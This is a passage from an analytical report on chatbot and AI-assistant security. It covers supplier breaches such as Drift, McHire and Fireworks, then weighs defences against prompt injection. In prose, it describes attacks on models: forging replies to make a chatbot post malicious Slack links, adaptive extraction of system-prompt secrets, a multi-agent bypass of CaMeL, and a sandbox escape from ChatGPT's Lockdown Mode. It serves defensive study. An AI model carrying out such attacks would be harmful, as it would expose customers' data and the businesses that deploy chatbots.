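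Okta also recommends tying each token to a cryptographic key held by the program that requested it, so that a stolen copy is useless on another computer. But an attacker who stays inside the supplier's servers could still send requests from an approved address, and perhaps use the key as well. The attacker in this case had been inside Drift's cloud systems but sent the requests to Okta from somewhere else.

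### McHire: 64 million records reachable, seven downloaded

A chatbot supplier can also expose its customers' data without losing any tokens. About 90% of McDonald's franchisees recruit through McHire, a website where Paradox.ai's chatbot, Olivia, collects applicants' contact details and the shifts they can work. *Would you like an IDOR with that?*, a post on ian.sh by security researchers Ian Carroll and Sam Curry, describes how they got into McHire.

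They first applied for a job and tried prompt injection on Olivia. This failed, apparently because the chatbot could give only preset responses. They then found a login page for Paradox.ai's staff and entered "123456" as both the username and the password, which gave them administrator access to a test restaurant.

When the researchers opened their own test application, they saw the page request it by a number, about 64,185,742. They lowered the number and received another applicant's details. An order lookup that accepts any order number has the same flaw, but here there was no model between the visitor and the database. Each reply could include the applicant's name, email address, phone number and home address, as well as a token that would let the researchers log in as the applicant and read the original chat.

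Carroll and Curry write that they could have retrieved the personal data of more than 64 million applicants. Paradox.ai's *Responsible Security Update* (2025) agrees that the researchers briefly had access to a system containing every chat, but says that most of the records were not tied to a candidate and contained no personal information. The researchers' figure matches the highest record number they saw, so it probably counts records rather than people. One person may also have applied several times.

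The researchers downloaded seven records, five of which contained personal information. According to Communications of the ACM, McDonald's said the effect was limited because the researchers had viewed only five. That number reflects the researchers' care and doesn't measure how much they could have taken.

Paradox.ai is confident that nobody else used the test account, which had been idle since 2019. But Carroll and Curry say that anyone with a McHire account and access to an inbox could have changed the number in the same way. The company's statement doesn't rule out misuse through a restaurant's own account, though there is no public evidence of it.

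Paradox.ai canceled the password within two hours of the report and confirmed the next day that it had fixed both problems, stressing that they affected only one client. Other clients still had reason to worry because of a separate incident. Krebs on Security (2025) found that malware on a Paradox.ai developer's personal computer had stolen hundreds of passwords in June 2025. The developer had at one point used the same seven-digit password for the accounts of several large clients, including Pepsi and Lockheed Martin.

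Paradox.ai replied that few of the passwords still worked and that it had required a central login with a second factor since 2020. The malware had also taken the developer's password for that central login and a cookie set to expire in December. A thief can sometimes use such a cookie to skip the second factor, although the server may reject it before it expires. Krebs on Security did not report anyone using the cookie to reach clients' data.

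### Chat logs at model suppliers and gateways

A company that gets its chatbot from a careful supplier may still depend on other companies the supplier uses. Many chatbots send requests to a company that runs models for others, or through a gateway that forwards them to several model makers. These companies can read the prompts and may keep them.

The best-documented case of 2026 involves Fireworks AI, which runs models for more than 10,000 customers. *AI company Fireworks says hackers stole data, billing info during October breaches* (Greig, 2026) reports that criminals broke in twice in October and stole billing information, datasets and secrets that give access to other systems. The second break-in started at a cloud company that hosted Fireworks' development computers.

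Notion, whose workplace software includes an AI assistant, was one of Fireworks' customers. Notion's *Fireworks AI incident* (2026) says that the stolen data included conversations with the assistant from fewer than 1% of workspaces. Most of the conversations had no label showing who wrote them, and they didn't include the results of tool calls. Notion had sent them to Fireworks to be classified rather than to answer users' questions. The classification was for a feature called Insights, which shows customers how they use AI.

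Fireworks should not have had the Notion AI chats that were stolen in the attack. *Notion-AI-Chats beim Fireworks-Angriff erbeutet* (Cornelißen, 2026) quotes Notion's help page, which says Fireworks had promised in its contract to keep no data. During the investigation, Notion learned that "data was retained from the Fireworks endpoints that we used."

As with Drift, the first report understated the damage. On November 2, Fireworks told Notion that the attackers had accessed a small set of data, which turned out to be invented test material. Notion disconnected from Fireworks the next morning and deleted its data there a day later. On November 6, Fireworks warned that the attackers might also have customers' data, and Notion began contacting affected customers on November 9. It advised them to replace any passwords or keys they had pasted into the assistant. According to *Notion Breach Fallout*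 (Gonzales, 2026), Notion has since reported that the breach exposed API keys for other companies' services.

Two other companies, Uber and Cursor, traced break-ins to Fireworks. Marc David's *Fireworks AI Breach* (2026) reports that an attacker used Fireworks' credentials to read driver's license data in a cloud system that Uber had built for Fireworks. At Cursor, which makes a coding assistant, the attacker used a key issued to Fireworks to get into stored records of AI agents' work, then used other credentials in those records to tamper with a programming extension that Cursor distributed.

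Fireworks wasn't the only target. Read and McCarthy (2026), in *“Black October” for AI Developer Platforms*, count at least nine such platforms that disclosed incidents in October. They link the attacks to "LLMjacking", the theft of access to paid models. A visitor who gets a shop's chatbot to do their homework also takes some of this access, but only through the chatbot's replies. A stolen key gives direct access to the model and can be resold. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *The Rise of LLMJacking* (2026) describes underground markets for these credentials and victims with fraudulent cloud bills in the hundreds of thousands. Attackers looking only for keys may also obtain chats.

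In October 2026, researchers found that 302.ai had left a store of files open to the internet, so nobody had to break in to reach them. Fadilpašić's *Security breach at AI aggregator exposes over 18 million files* (2026) describes 302.ai as an AI aggregator. Tech Times UK's *AI Data Leak Exposes 22.7TB of Files* (2026) puts the total at 17.6 million files, including more than 144,000 chat logs with personal information. Some of the logs were support conversations about sex dolls. No one has confirmed that a malicious outsider copied the files.

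An experiment by the security company Dragos suggests that published breaches are only part of the problem. BagheeraAltered (2026) describes the experiment in *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them*. Between July and November, Dragos's researchers sent about two million prompts to popular AI services, each containing a unique web address and credentials planted as bait. Outsiders later visited some of the addresses and used some of the credentials for Amazon's cloud. An automated scanner might visit an address harmlessly, but it is harder to think of an innocent reason to use someone else's credentials. Dragos reported evidence that some providers had been compromised and that companies in model marketplaces had read customers' prompts without permission.

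### Is it a chatbot risk if the model played no part?

Stealing the Drift tokens, reading the McHire records and copying Notion's conversations did not require tricking a language model, so one could reasonably call these ordinary supplier breaches and leave them out of an account of chatbot security.

The same thefts happen without chatbots. In October 2025, attackers stole tokens from Gainsight, which sells software for managing customer relationships, and used them to enter its customers' Salesforce systems. Okta's *First Drift, now Gainsight* (2025) says that the same address restrictions protected Okta again. A year later, an attacker used credentials from the cloud account of Qubole, a data-processing company, to enter the cloud systems of customers that had set up their accounts to trust Qubole's (Morrow, Johnstone and Read, *Trusted by Default*, 2026).

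But a company deciding whether to deploy a chatbot needs to know what it might lose, whether or not the model is to blame. It can ask what would have happened with an ordinary web form instead.

| Case | With a web form instead of a chatbot |
|---|---|
| Cloudflare's support cases, stolen through Drift | The cases would still exist, but Drift would have no token to read them |
| Applicants' details in McHire | Probably the same exposure, because a form would collect much the same details |
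| Conversations with Notion's assistant | The conversations would not exist |

Drift is a chatbot risk in this sense because of the access its token gave. A contact form only has to add records to Salesforce, so it can work without read access. A chatbot that recognizes returning customers or answers questions about their accounts also has to read records, and its supplier usually holds the credential for doing so. A company could give a web form the same broad access but would have less reason to.

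McHire is a weaker example, because the password and the record numbers would have been just as dangerous behind a web form, and the fixes have been known for decades. The main lesson for deployers is that testing the chatbot would not have found the problem. Paradox.ai admitted that its own penetration tests had missed the flaw in the record lookup.

The Notion case has the closest connection to chatbots, because the assistant created the data that leaked. A form collects an order number and little else, but in a chat window Ines might mention that she needs the kettle by Friday because she is going into hospital, or that the house will be empty for two weeks. The shop needs neither fact for long, but both stay in the transcript until somebody deletes it.

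Deploying a chatbot adds a supplier, though it doesn't change who can open the shop's Salesforce records by other routes or how well the shop protects its staff's passwords. That supplier can then add others. Salesloft's website lists three more companies that began processing data in 2026 for its services, which include Drift. Two of them sell AI chat products. A customer that reviewed Drift's security in 2025 would have to look at those companies as well.

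Removing the chatbot doesn't undo all of this. Zscaler's security chief told CyberScoop that the company was already ending its relationship with Salesloft, for unrelated reasons, when the attacker took its data. If Tallow Lane deletes the chat window from its website, the supplier's token may still open the shop's customer records, and the old conversations may still be on the supplier's server. The shop also has to cancel the token in Salesforce and get the supplier to delete the transcripts, including any copies it sent to other companies.

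## Defences and how well they hold

Cancelling a former supplier's token and deleting old transcripts reduces what a shop can lose, but people can still try to mislead its chatbot. Some defences make the model less likely to produce a harmful output, while others limit what a harmful output can do. Suppose a visitor tries to talk Tallow Lane's chatbot into a $500 refund for a $38 kettle. A well-trained model will probably refuse, and a refund tool that never returns more than the customer paid will block the refund even if the model agrees.

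A deployer can check the refund tool by reading its code, but can measure the model's resistance only by how often the model withstands the attacks that testers thought of.

### Training models to rank instructions

Model makers teach the instruction hierarchy with examples of users trying to override the system prompt. They pair each example with the reply they want, such as a polite refusal, and adjust the model until it tends to write similar replies.

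*A Closer Look at System Prompt Robustness* (2025) measured the effect of such training on Llama 3.1 8B, a small model from Meta. The test used the easiest tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent does jobs such as paying a bill while reading text that contains hostile instructions. Training cut the attack success rate from 4.2% to 0.9% and raised the share of user tasks the model completed from 25% to 32%. A further stage of training cut attack success to zero, but task completion fell to 28%.

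The large companies publish similar figures in system cards, the documents that accompany new models. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* describes OpenAI's August 2026 update for three versions of GPT-5.6. Direct attacks written by GPT-Red, a model OpenAI trained to find them, succeeded about 0.05% of the time against one version, Sol. Instructions hidden in emails, files and web pages succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol and 2.94% of the time against Luna, the most resistant version. OpenAI measured these rates in its own test environments, so they don't give the chance of a breach in a real product.

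Anthropic's figures vary more. VentureBeat reports that attacks on a browser agent running Claude Opus 4.8, released in May 2026, succeeded in 31.5% of attempts without added safeguards and 0.5% with them. Attacks on the older Sonnet 4.6 had succeeded 50.7% of the time without safeguards. In June, Anthropic said Mythos 5 had the best result so far on an outside prompt injection benchmark from Gray Swan.

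A deployer can't use these figures to rank the two companies, because they tested different products with different attacks and have both released newer models since. The figures suggest that resistance is improving, and that a deployer should look for a test close to its own use. A support chatbot that only answers visitors' questions faces mostly direct attacks, while an assistant that reads email faces attacks hidden in the messages, which succeeded far more often in OpenAI's tests.

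### What a stricter system prompt protects

A deployer usually can't retrain a rented model, but it can write a stricter system prompt. Kaya and colleagues tested three system prompts on the chatbot in their simulated water bottle shop. An ordinary visitor's message got the chatbot to write a program in 10% of trials with the loosest prompt, averaged over 11 models, and in none with either of the two stricter prompts.

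The same prompts did not protect a tool. The researchers gave the chatbot a tool that posted a message to a particular Slack channel whenever a visitor mentioned certain topics. They then tried to make the chatbot post a malicious link in a channel that the whole company could read. Attacks sent as ordinary visitor messages succeeded in 37% of trials with the loosest prompt, 38% with the stricter one and 37% with the strictest. Nearly all these successes were against Google's and Anthropic's models. When the attacker could forge an earlier chatbot reply, the success rate rose from 48% with the loosest prompt to 71% with the strictest.

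A rule against unrelated work doesn't address this attack, because posting to Slack is part of the chatbot's job. The researchers then had a language model add rules to the tool's instructions, such as using only the preset channel and topics. Attack success fell by 40–75%. Setting the channel in code and accepting only topics from a list could work better, because the model would have no way to choose another channel or include a link.

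Xie, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Securing LLM-as-a-Service for Small Businesses*, report much better results for defensive prompts. They built a chatbot platform for small companies and tested it with a real shop, All Table Sports Australia, using 250 genuine customer questions and 250 attacks. Instructions added to the system prompt ("guard prompts") caught 99.6–100% of the attacks on three models without flagging any genuine questions.

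This result is less impressive than it sounds, because the researchers had refined the guard prompts by testing them repeatedly against known attack patterns. The 250 attacks came from an existing collection and did not change when they failed. Xie and colleagues warn that the prompts may not work as well for other businesses or against new attacks. Their guard prompt also tells the model to act as a security classifier and lists warning signs to look for. The test therefore measured how well a model recognizes familiar attacks, not how well a chatbot protects its tools while helping a customer.

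### Classifiers and false alarms

A classifier, like the one EchoLeak's instructions got past, learns from examples of attacks and ordinary messages. It typically scores each new message, and the deployer sets the threshold score at which the software blocks a message. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also blocks more messages from honest customers.

Attacks are rare, so even an accurate classifier can produce mostly false alarms. Suppose a large supplier handles a million chats a day, 100 of which are attacks. Its classifier detects 99% of them and wrongly flags 1% of honest chats.

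| | Chats | Alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks | 100 | 99 |
| Honest chats | 999,900 | 9,999 |
| Total | 1,000,000 | 10,098 |

Only about 1% of the chats the filter flags are attacks, and it still misses one attack a day. If it blocks every chat it flags, it turns away about 10,000 honest customers a day. If employees spend a minute checking each flagged chat instead, the work takes 168 hours each day, or 21 people working eight-hour shifts.

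The detector that Xie and colleagues tested alongside their guard prompts caught 81.6% of the attacks and, going by their figures, wrongly flagged one of the 250 honest questions. Half of the messages in their test were attacks, so 204 of the detector's 205 alarms were real. In the supplier's traffic, the same detector would catch about 82 attacks and raise about 4,000 false alarms a day, so only about 2% of its alarms would be real. The false alarm rate is itself imprecise because it is based on a single mistake in 250 questions.

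The supplier can make better use of its alarms by combining them with other evidence, such as failed tool calls. David C recommends logging these because attackers usually need several attempts to get an attack right. For example, a flagged chat in which the refund tool has rejected four requests is worth reviewing, while one about kettle sizes can probably wait.

Classifiers can also make an assistant less useful. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports an AgentDojo test in which an agent running GPT-4o completed 61% of its users' tasks while under attack, but only 32% with an injection detector. If a detector rejects a whole email because it contains an attack, the assistant also loses anything useful in that email. In the same test, repeating the user's request after the retrieved text raised completion from 61% to 70%. The benchmark is flawed, because some of its attacks overwrite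 information the agent needs, which makes those tasks impossible.

### Attackers who try again

If each attempt succeeds with probability p and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If a defense stops 99% of attempts, an attacker who makes 300 attempts has a 1 − 0.99³⁰⁰, or about 95%, chance of succeeding at least once. At the 0.05% success rate that OpenAI measured for direct attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol, an attacker would need about 6,000 attempts to have the same chance. This is another reason to limit messages per visitor.

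Real attack attempts are not independent. VentureBeat reports that a single attempt against Claude Opus 4.6, an earlier model, succeeded 17.8% of the time when the model operated a computer through its screen without added safeguards. If attempts were independent, an attacker would have a 98% chance of succeeding at least once in 20 attempts, but the measured rate after 200 was 78.6%, probably because some test scenarios were much harder to attack than others. Added safeguards reduced the rate after 200 attempts to 57.1%. In a restricted coding environment, none of 200 attempts worked.

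Attackers also change their attacks after seeing how a defence responds. Adaptive testing, which does the same, has repeatedly broken published defences that looked strong against a fixed list of attacks.

*Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (Deep, Emmons and colleagues, 2026) shows how this happens. Most of the researchers work for Swept AI, which sells security testing for AI systems, and the paper recommends the company's product. The researchers put three secrets in a system prompt and had an AI attacker try to extract them from Gemini 2.5 Pro, with the model's built-in safety filters off. The attacker sent ten messages in each round, kept the most successful and rewrote them for the next. The table shows how long each defence lasted before a single reply gave away nearly everything.

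| Defense | Rounds until it failed |
|---|---|
| Screening visitors' messages with fixed patterns and a classifier | 39 |
| Security rules in the system prompt | 49 |
| Tags around the visitor's message | 84 |
| A written rule ranking the system prompt above the visitor | 247 |
| Security rules at both the start and the end of the prompt | 277 |
| Blocking replies that contain text from the system prompt | Still holding at 500 |

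None of these defences had failed completely after 25 rounds, so a short test would have made them all look fairly strong. The ranking rule in the table was only a sentence in the prompt, so its failure is weak evidence of how well instruction-hierarchy training works.

Blocking replies worked in all 15,000 attempts that tested it, but the experiment favored this defense because the filter looked for exact pieces of the system prompt and the researchers also counted leaks by looking for exact text. A secret spelled out with spaces between the letters would have passed the filter without being counted as a leak. The researchers acknowledge this and advise deployers to keep secrets out of prompts wherever possible.

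### Authorization outside the model

Output filters and permission checks don't depend on the model's judgment. Tallow Lane's order lookup takes the customer number from the login, and a retrieval system can filter passages by permission before the search. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give similar advice for a furniture shop's support chatbot. The software can ask customers to log in when the model tries to start a return, or block access to other customers' data for the whole session.

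Authorization is harder when the assistant reads text written by someone other than its user. David C recommends reducing the model's privileges to those of the person whose text it is processing, a rule that came out of an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista. Suppose Tomas asks Tallow Lane's helpdesk assistant to summarize an email from Ines. While the email is in the model's input, the assistant could look up Ines's orders but not what the shop pays for its kettles, so an instruction hidden in the email would give her no access she didn't already have.

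The rule limits what the assistant can do. If Tomas asks for a summary of 40 customers' emails, the assistant could not process them together, because no customer has the right to read the others' emails. It would have to summarize each customer's emails separately and let ordinary software combine the results. Tomas also couldn't ask it to draft a reply that uses the shop's internal notes.

### Designs that separate reading from acting

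Beurer-Kellner and colleagues turn this idea into six designs, all based on the principle that untrusted text that a model has read must not be able to trigger a harmful action.

| Design | How it works | What an attacker may still be able to do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | Trigger an action on the list |
| Plan then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads outside data | Change what an approved email says |
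| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get their own document misclassified |
| Dual model | One model plans and uses tools, while another without tools reads untrusted text | Corrupt the text that the second model writes |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program, which then handles the untrusted data | Corrupt the data that passes through the program |
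| Context minimization | The software removes the user's message before the model writes its answer | Influence which information the chatbot looks up |

In the furniture shop example, the chatbot's document store is assumed to contain no customer reviews, so the main danger is the text that visitors type. An attacker might trick a customer into pasting a hostile prompt that makes the chatbot look up the customer's data and leak it through a link or an image. A visitor might also get the chatbot to say something embarrassing, then post a screenshot of it publicly.

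The simplest of the three designs they consider uses a classifier to decide whether each message is about furniture. A visitor can defeat this by asking about a sofa and something unrelated in the same message, because the classifier makes a single decision about the whole message.

A stricter chatbot uses the action selector. The shop lists the requests it expects, such as canceling an order or asking for a sofa's price. The software turns a customer's message into a vector, as a retrieval system does, and checks whether it is close enough to a request on the list. If so, it carries out that request and sends the result straight to the customer. An attacker may be able to word a message to match the wrong request, but every request on the list should be safe. The chatbot will turn away reasonable requests that the shop didn't expect.

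With context minimization, the model can still write the answer. It first turns the customer's message into a query, such as a search for the price of a particular sofa. The software then deletes the message and gives the model only the cleaned-up query and its result. If the customer also demanded a 90% discount, that demand is gone when the model writes the answer. So is anything else left out of the query, such as a request to keep the explanation simple.

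The other four designs mainly protect a trustworthy user from untrusted documents, so they suit an employee's assistant better than a public chat window. The furniture shop's assumption about reviews also matters, because a shop whose crawler collects reviews must also protect the chatbot from its documents.

### CaMeL and its cost

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, is the best-known example of the code-then-execute design. Suppose Tomas asks an assistant built this way to send Noor a list of parcels that customers reported as damaged today.

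1. A planning model reads Tomas's request and the descriptions of the tools. It never sees the customers' emails.
2. It writes a short program that fetches today's emails, has a second model list the damaged parcels, and sends the list to Noor.
3. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. The second model reads the emails but has no tools.
4. The interpreter records where each piece of data came from and checks it against the company's rules before every tool call.

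An instruction in a customer's email can make the list wrong, but it can't add a step that sends the list to someone else. Some plans need an address from an email, such as when Tomas asks the assistant to reply to a customer. For these plans, the rules in the last step let the interpreter block company data from being sent to an address that came from outside.

The planning model has to finish its program without seeing the data, so it can't plan for a request such as "do whatever Ines asks in her latest email," where the steps depend on what she wrote. Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks with its security guarantees in place, compared with 84% for an agent without the defence. CaMeL therefore completed about one-twelfth fewer tasks. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes the performance as comparable and reports that CaMeL stopped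 nearly all the attacks in the benchmark.

The guarantee can fail when several agents work together. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes a test on a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL. The researchers asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack, and planted an instruction in the applicant database. The first two agents treated the database text as untrusted data. The coordinating agent then put the summary into its request to the third agent, which handled messages. The third agent treated the whole request as trusted instructions from its user. Its planning model therefore read the planted text and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

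The researchers fixed this by having agents pass instructions and untrusted data to each other separately. In their tests on five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the new method. The new method also reduced the number of tasks the agents completed, but only modestly for the strongest models.

Even a perfect version of CaMeL would trust its user. That is reasonable for Tomas but not for an anonymous visitor, who can ask for a harmful plan. It also can't verify retrieved statements, so it doesn't protect against planted facts.

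### Limits on where data can go

A company can often restrict outside communication, one of the three conditions in Willison's lethal trifecta, without removing the assistant's access to documents. It can block images from other websites, remove links from answers, or let the assistant contact only approved addresses.

OpenAI added such a control, Lockdown Mode, to ChatGPT in June 2026. This optional setting limits ChatGPT's requests to outside servers, so a successful prompt injection has fewer ways to send data out. The Hacker News quotes OpenAI's warning that the setting works "at the expense of disabling or limiting some useful features."

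The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) describes how the security company Check Point got around ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode. ChatGPT can display a preview of a web page inside a conversation. The preview runs in a sandbox, an isolated frame that can't read the app's cookies or contact outside servers without the user's consent. ChatGPT intercepted direct attempts to open a new window from the preview, but the sandbox's settings still allowed new windows. The researchers created another frame inside the preview, which gave them a way to open windows that ChatGPT didn't intercept. The new window was free of the sandbox's restrictions and could send data out.

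An attacker could have delivered the page through a crafted prompt, a shared chat or a malicious GPT (a customized version of ChatGPT). In the desktop app, the theft required no click. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026, and the report mentions no victims. A week before Check Point's disclosure, another company, Parameter Labs, published a different flaw in the same preview feature. It let an attacker take over the account of someone who opened a shared chat and clicked on the preview.

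Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (March 2026) described an earlier gap in ChatGPT's limits, a route to the internet from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt could use this route to send out a user's messages and uploaded files.

Outbound limits also fail, but their failures are easier to fix than a model's. Once OpenAI closed the route through the preview, rewording the prompt would not reopen it.

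### When a person has to approve

Software can also ask a person to approve a risky action before carrying it out. This works best when the action is rare, its details are easy to check, and the person approving it has a reason to refuse. An employee at a kettle shop who sees a request for a $4,200 refund to a customer will probably question it.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend having a person confirm sensitive actions, but warn that tired or overloaded people may approve unsafe ones. Someone who approves 200 routine emails a day is unlikely to read the last 50 carefully. A long email is also harder to check through a voice assistant than on a screen.

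Even a careful reviewer can miss an attack that isn't visible. A hostile instruction might make the assistant hide company data in a draft reply, using invisible characters. The reviewer would see only a polite answer to the customer and send it. Ordinary software should remove such characters before the reviewer sees the draft.

The approval screen should also take the order, amount and destination card directly from a reliable source, such as Tallow Lane's database. If the model writes the summary that Tomas sees, an attacker who has misled the model may control the summary too. The software also has to confirm that the approval came from Tomas, because attackers have forged approvals and approved their own requests while impersonating an administrator.

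The shop can keep the number of approval requests manageable by letting software approve any action it can verify against the shop's records. A $38 refund to the original card for an undelivered parcel may not need human review, but a large refund that follows a change of email address does. With a planning design such as CaMeL, Tomas could also approve the whole plan once instead of confirming each step, though he would still need to check any data the plan sends out.

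### Can prompt injection ever be fixed?

In a December 2025 post for the National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that prompt injection may never be prevented as completely as SQL injection, because language models have no built-in distinction between instructions and data. Detecting attacks, training models to prioritize instructions and marking text as data are all attempts to add that distinction. These methods can make attacks harder, but David C advises companies to be wary of any product sold as a way to stop them.

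On this view, companies should treat prompt injection as a permanent risk and reduce its likelihood and impact. If the remaining risk is unacceptable for a system, a language model may not be suitable for it. David C's concern comes partly from the history of SQL injection, which researchers described in the 1990s. Attacks peaked only around 2010, after many websites had come to depend on unprotected databases, and better defaults followed a decade of data leaks.

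This post recommends the design-patterns paper and CaMeL, which appeared before it but suggest a partial answer to it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues agree that general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while they depend on current language models. They point out that researchers have worked on a similar problem in image recognition for more than a decade without solving it. But they think a system can be secure even if the model inside it is vulnerable.

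Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection without having to recognise hostile text. CaMeL takes a similar approach to prompt injection by fixing the plan before any model reads untrusted data. This comes close to stopping injected text from changing which actions the system takes, but it makes some tasks impossible and works only if every connection between agents keeps the plan separate from untrusted data. Injected text can still alter a summary or an answer, because its content has to depend on what the model reads.

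Another possible reply is that model makers may reduce the success rate of attacks until it hardly matters. Companies already manage the risk of fraudulent emails without having eliminated them. This argument is reasonable for a chatbot that only gives advice about kettles, where one success in 2,000 attempts would do little harm. It is much weaker for a system in which a single success exposes every customer's records, because an attacker can make thousands of attempts.

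David C's argument also applies only to models that work as current ones do. A future model might process instructions and data through separate mechanisms, but retrieved text would still have to influence its answers.

Tallow Lane can secure its order lookup now, without such a model, by tying it to the login. It has no equally reliable protection for an assistant that reads strangers' emails, searches every customer's records and writes to any address. By David C's test, the shop should narrow that assistant's job unless it can accept the occasional theft.

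## Deployment scale against the maturity of security tooling

Someone at Tallow Lane has to know which assistants the shop runs and what each one can access before the shop can narrow an assistant's job. Security companies often complain that businesses have deployed chatbots faster than they have learned to secure them. The complaint matters only if chatbots are numerous and spreading, the tools and habits for securing them are still poor, and people are being harmed as a result.

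### Counting chatbots

Nobody has counted all the production chatbots in use, and the available figures count different things.

Kaya and colleagues found the 17 chatbot plugins they studied mentioned in the page code of 10,417 websites in August 2024 and 17,474 in April 2025, a rise of 68%. Two of the plugins, with 1,182 sites between them in April, have no figure for August, and leaving them out lowers the rise to 56%. When the researchers visited 200 of the sites, a chatbot answered on 125. At that rate, there were about 6,500 working chatbots in August 2024 and 10,900 in April 2025. The sites included those of local governments, universities and international airports. The true number of chatbots must be much higher, because the study left out the enterprise platforms that larger companies use.

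*Pwn the Enterprise*, a post about Zenity's 2025 talk at the Black Hat security conference, reports that the company's researchers found more than 3,500 Copilot Studio agents on the internet. These agents can take actions, and the count covers only those an outsider could locate. The researchers demonstrated the risk by attacking a copy of one agent, so nobody knows how many of the others would have leaked their data.

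The research company Gartner (2026) surveyed 199 customer-service leaders in April and May and found that spending on AI had risen 38% while their departments' budgets had risen 2%. In an earlier survey of 321 such leaders, Gartner (2026) found that 91% felt pressure from senior executives to introduce AI.

A Gartner (2026) survey of 3,566 customers found that their use of company chatbots had not changed measurably since 2022. They were about three times as likely to take a service problem to another company's AI tool. These findings weaken the claim of rapid growth, but a little-used chatbot can be as useful to an attacker as a popular one. Gartner also advises companies to build services that can act for customers, for example by updating their accounts. Following this advice would give each chatbot more power, even if no more customers used it.

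Salesforce's filings cover a single platform, Agentforce. Salesforce (2025) had signed more than 18,500 Agentforce deals by December 2025, about 9,500 of them paid. Salesforce Ben reported that about 12,000 of the company's 150,000 customers, or 8%, had adopted the product that autumn. A year later, Salesforce reported 7.2 billion tasks in one quarter, up from 4 billion in the previous quarter. EconoTimes' *Salesforce Raises Revenue Outlook as AI Use Grows in Fiscal Q3* (2026) attributes those tasks to "AI agents and features", so the total probably includes a lot of work done by something other than customer-facing agents. Faisal (2026), in *Salesforce Stops Reporting AI Revenue After Four Quarters*, points out that the task count replaced Agentforce's revenue, which had passed $1.5 billion a year and was still rising.

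More websites now have chatbots, companies spend more on AI, and their agents do more work. The evidence doesn't show that customers talk to company chatbots more than they used to.

### Signs of maturity

"Maturity" is a vague word, so it helps to judge it by things an outsider could check. A company with mature security keeps a list of its chatbots, tests each one before release, and has logs that would reveal an attack. Its suppliers give flaws public identifiers and release fixes that still work when an attack is reworded. Agreed standards also exist for the company to check its work against.

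Many small deployers don't seem to keep track of their chatbots. Of the 200 websites that Kaya and colleagues visited, 37 displayed a chatbot that didn't work, and another 18 still had a plugin's code on the page but no visible chatbot. At larger companies, suppliers add AI to software that the company approved years ago. Dave Gerry, who runs the bug bounty company Bugcrowd, told Axios that such tools had "magically got AI turned on" (*Your agents can be hacked by other agents*). A list of chatbots made when the company bought the software would not include these tools.

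The best evidence on testing comes from bug bounty programs, in which companies pay outsiders to find flaws. HackerOne, which runs many of them, had 1,121 programs that covered AI in 2025, an increase of 270% in a year. HackerOne (2026) later found that valid reports of AI flaws had grown 222% in two years, and that reports of system prompt leaks had grown 557%. These increases don't show that chatbots became less secure, because the growth in programs may only mean that more people were looking for flaws.

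HackerOne's figures are good news about testing, but bounty hunters mostly examine products that customers already use, and the figures don't show how many companies test a chatbot before release. Companies that do test can still miss flaws, as Paradox.ai did with McHire.

Logging is weaker. The eight plugins that accepted forged conversation histories did not show the forged messages in website owners' dashboards. With three of them, owners could have used the site's API key to find the messages in the model provider's logs, but with the other five, owners had no log that showed them.

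Public identifiers let a company look up whether a flaw affects its software and whether anyone has exploited it. EchoLeak, SearchLeak, ShareLeak and BodySnatcher all have CVE numbers, which is a sign of progress. The system works less well when the supplier blames the customer's settings, as Salesforce did with PipeLeak, or closes a report without announcing a fix. *Pwn the Enterprise* describes an attack on Einstein, Salesforce's assistant, that began with a support case sent through a public form. When an employee asked about open cases, the assistant changed every customer contact's email address to one the attacker had chosen. Salesforce replied that it already knew of the problem and was working on a fix, then closed the researchers' case without giving a date. A mistake in a single deployer's own code, such as an order lookup that accepts any order number, normally gets no identifier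 because nobody else runs that code.

Fixes that depend on recognizing an attack often don't last. The same post lists the flaws that Zenity found in ChatGPT and Copilot Studio as "fixed (injection we used no longer works)". An attack that Zenity demonstrated on Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2024 still worked a year later, and the researchers switched from email to a calendar invitation only for variety. The dispute over whether Microsoft's patch for ShareLeak fully worked concerns the same problem.

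Companies are fixing flaws faster across software in general. HackerOne found that the average time to fix a flaw fell from 135 days to 62 in two years. Over the same period, the number of valid reports still awaiting a fix rose 131%, because researchers found flaws faster than companies repaired them. Neither figure is specific to AI.

### Standards from OWASP and NIST

OWASP has published a lot of guidance quickly. It released a list of the top ten risks for AI agents in December 2025, and its separate list for language-model applications reached a third edition in August 2026. According to Infosecurity Magazine, OWASP also added a framework in June for assessing the maturity of a company's controls on agents. In September, OWASP (2026) announced that it had taken over the Agent Control Standard, for enforcing limits on agents while they run.

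The US government has moved more slowly. NIST's main catalog of security controls, SP 800-53, covers all kinds of computer systems, and NIST plans "overlays" that would adapt it to AI. NIST's *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems* lists five planned uses, including language-model assistants and single agents. The title uses "super intelligence" because an executive order of September 2026 made agencies replace "artificial intelligence" with that term. By October 20, 2026, more than a year after the concept paper, NIST had published only an outline for one of the five uses, predictive AI, which includes software that forecasts demand.

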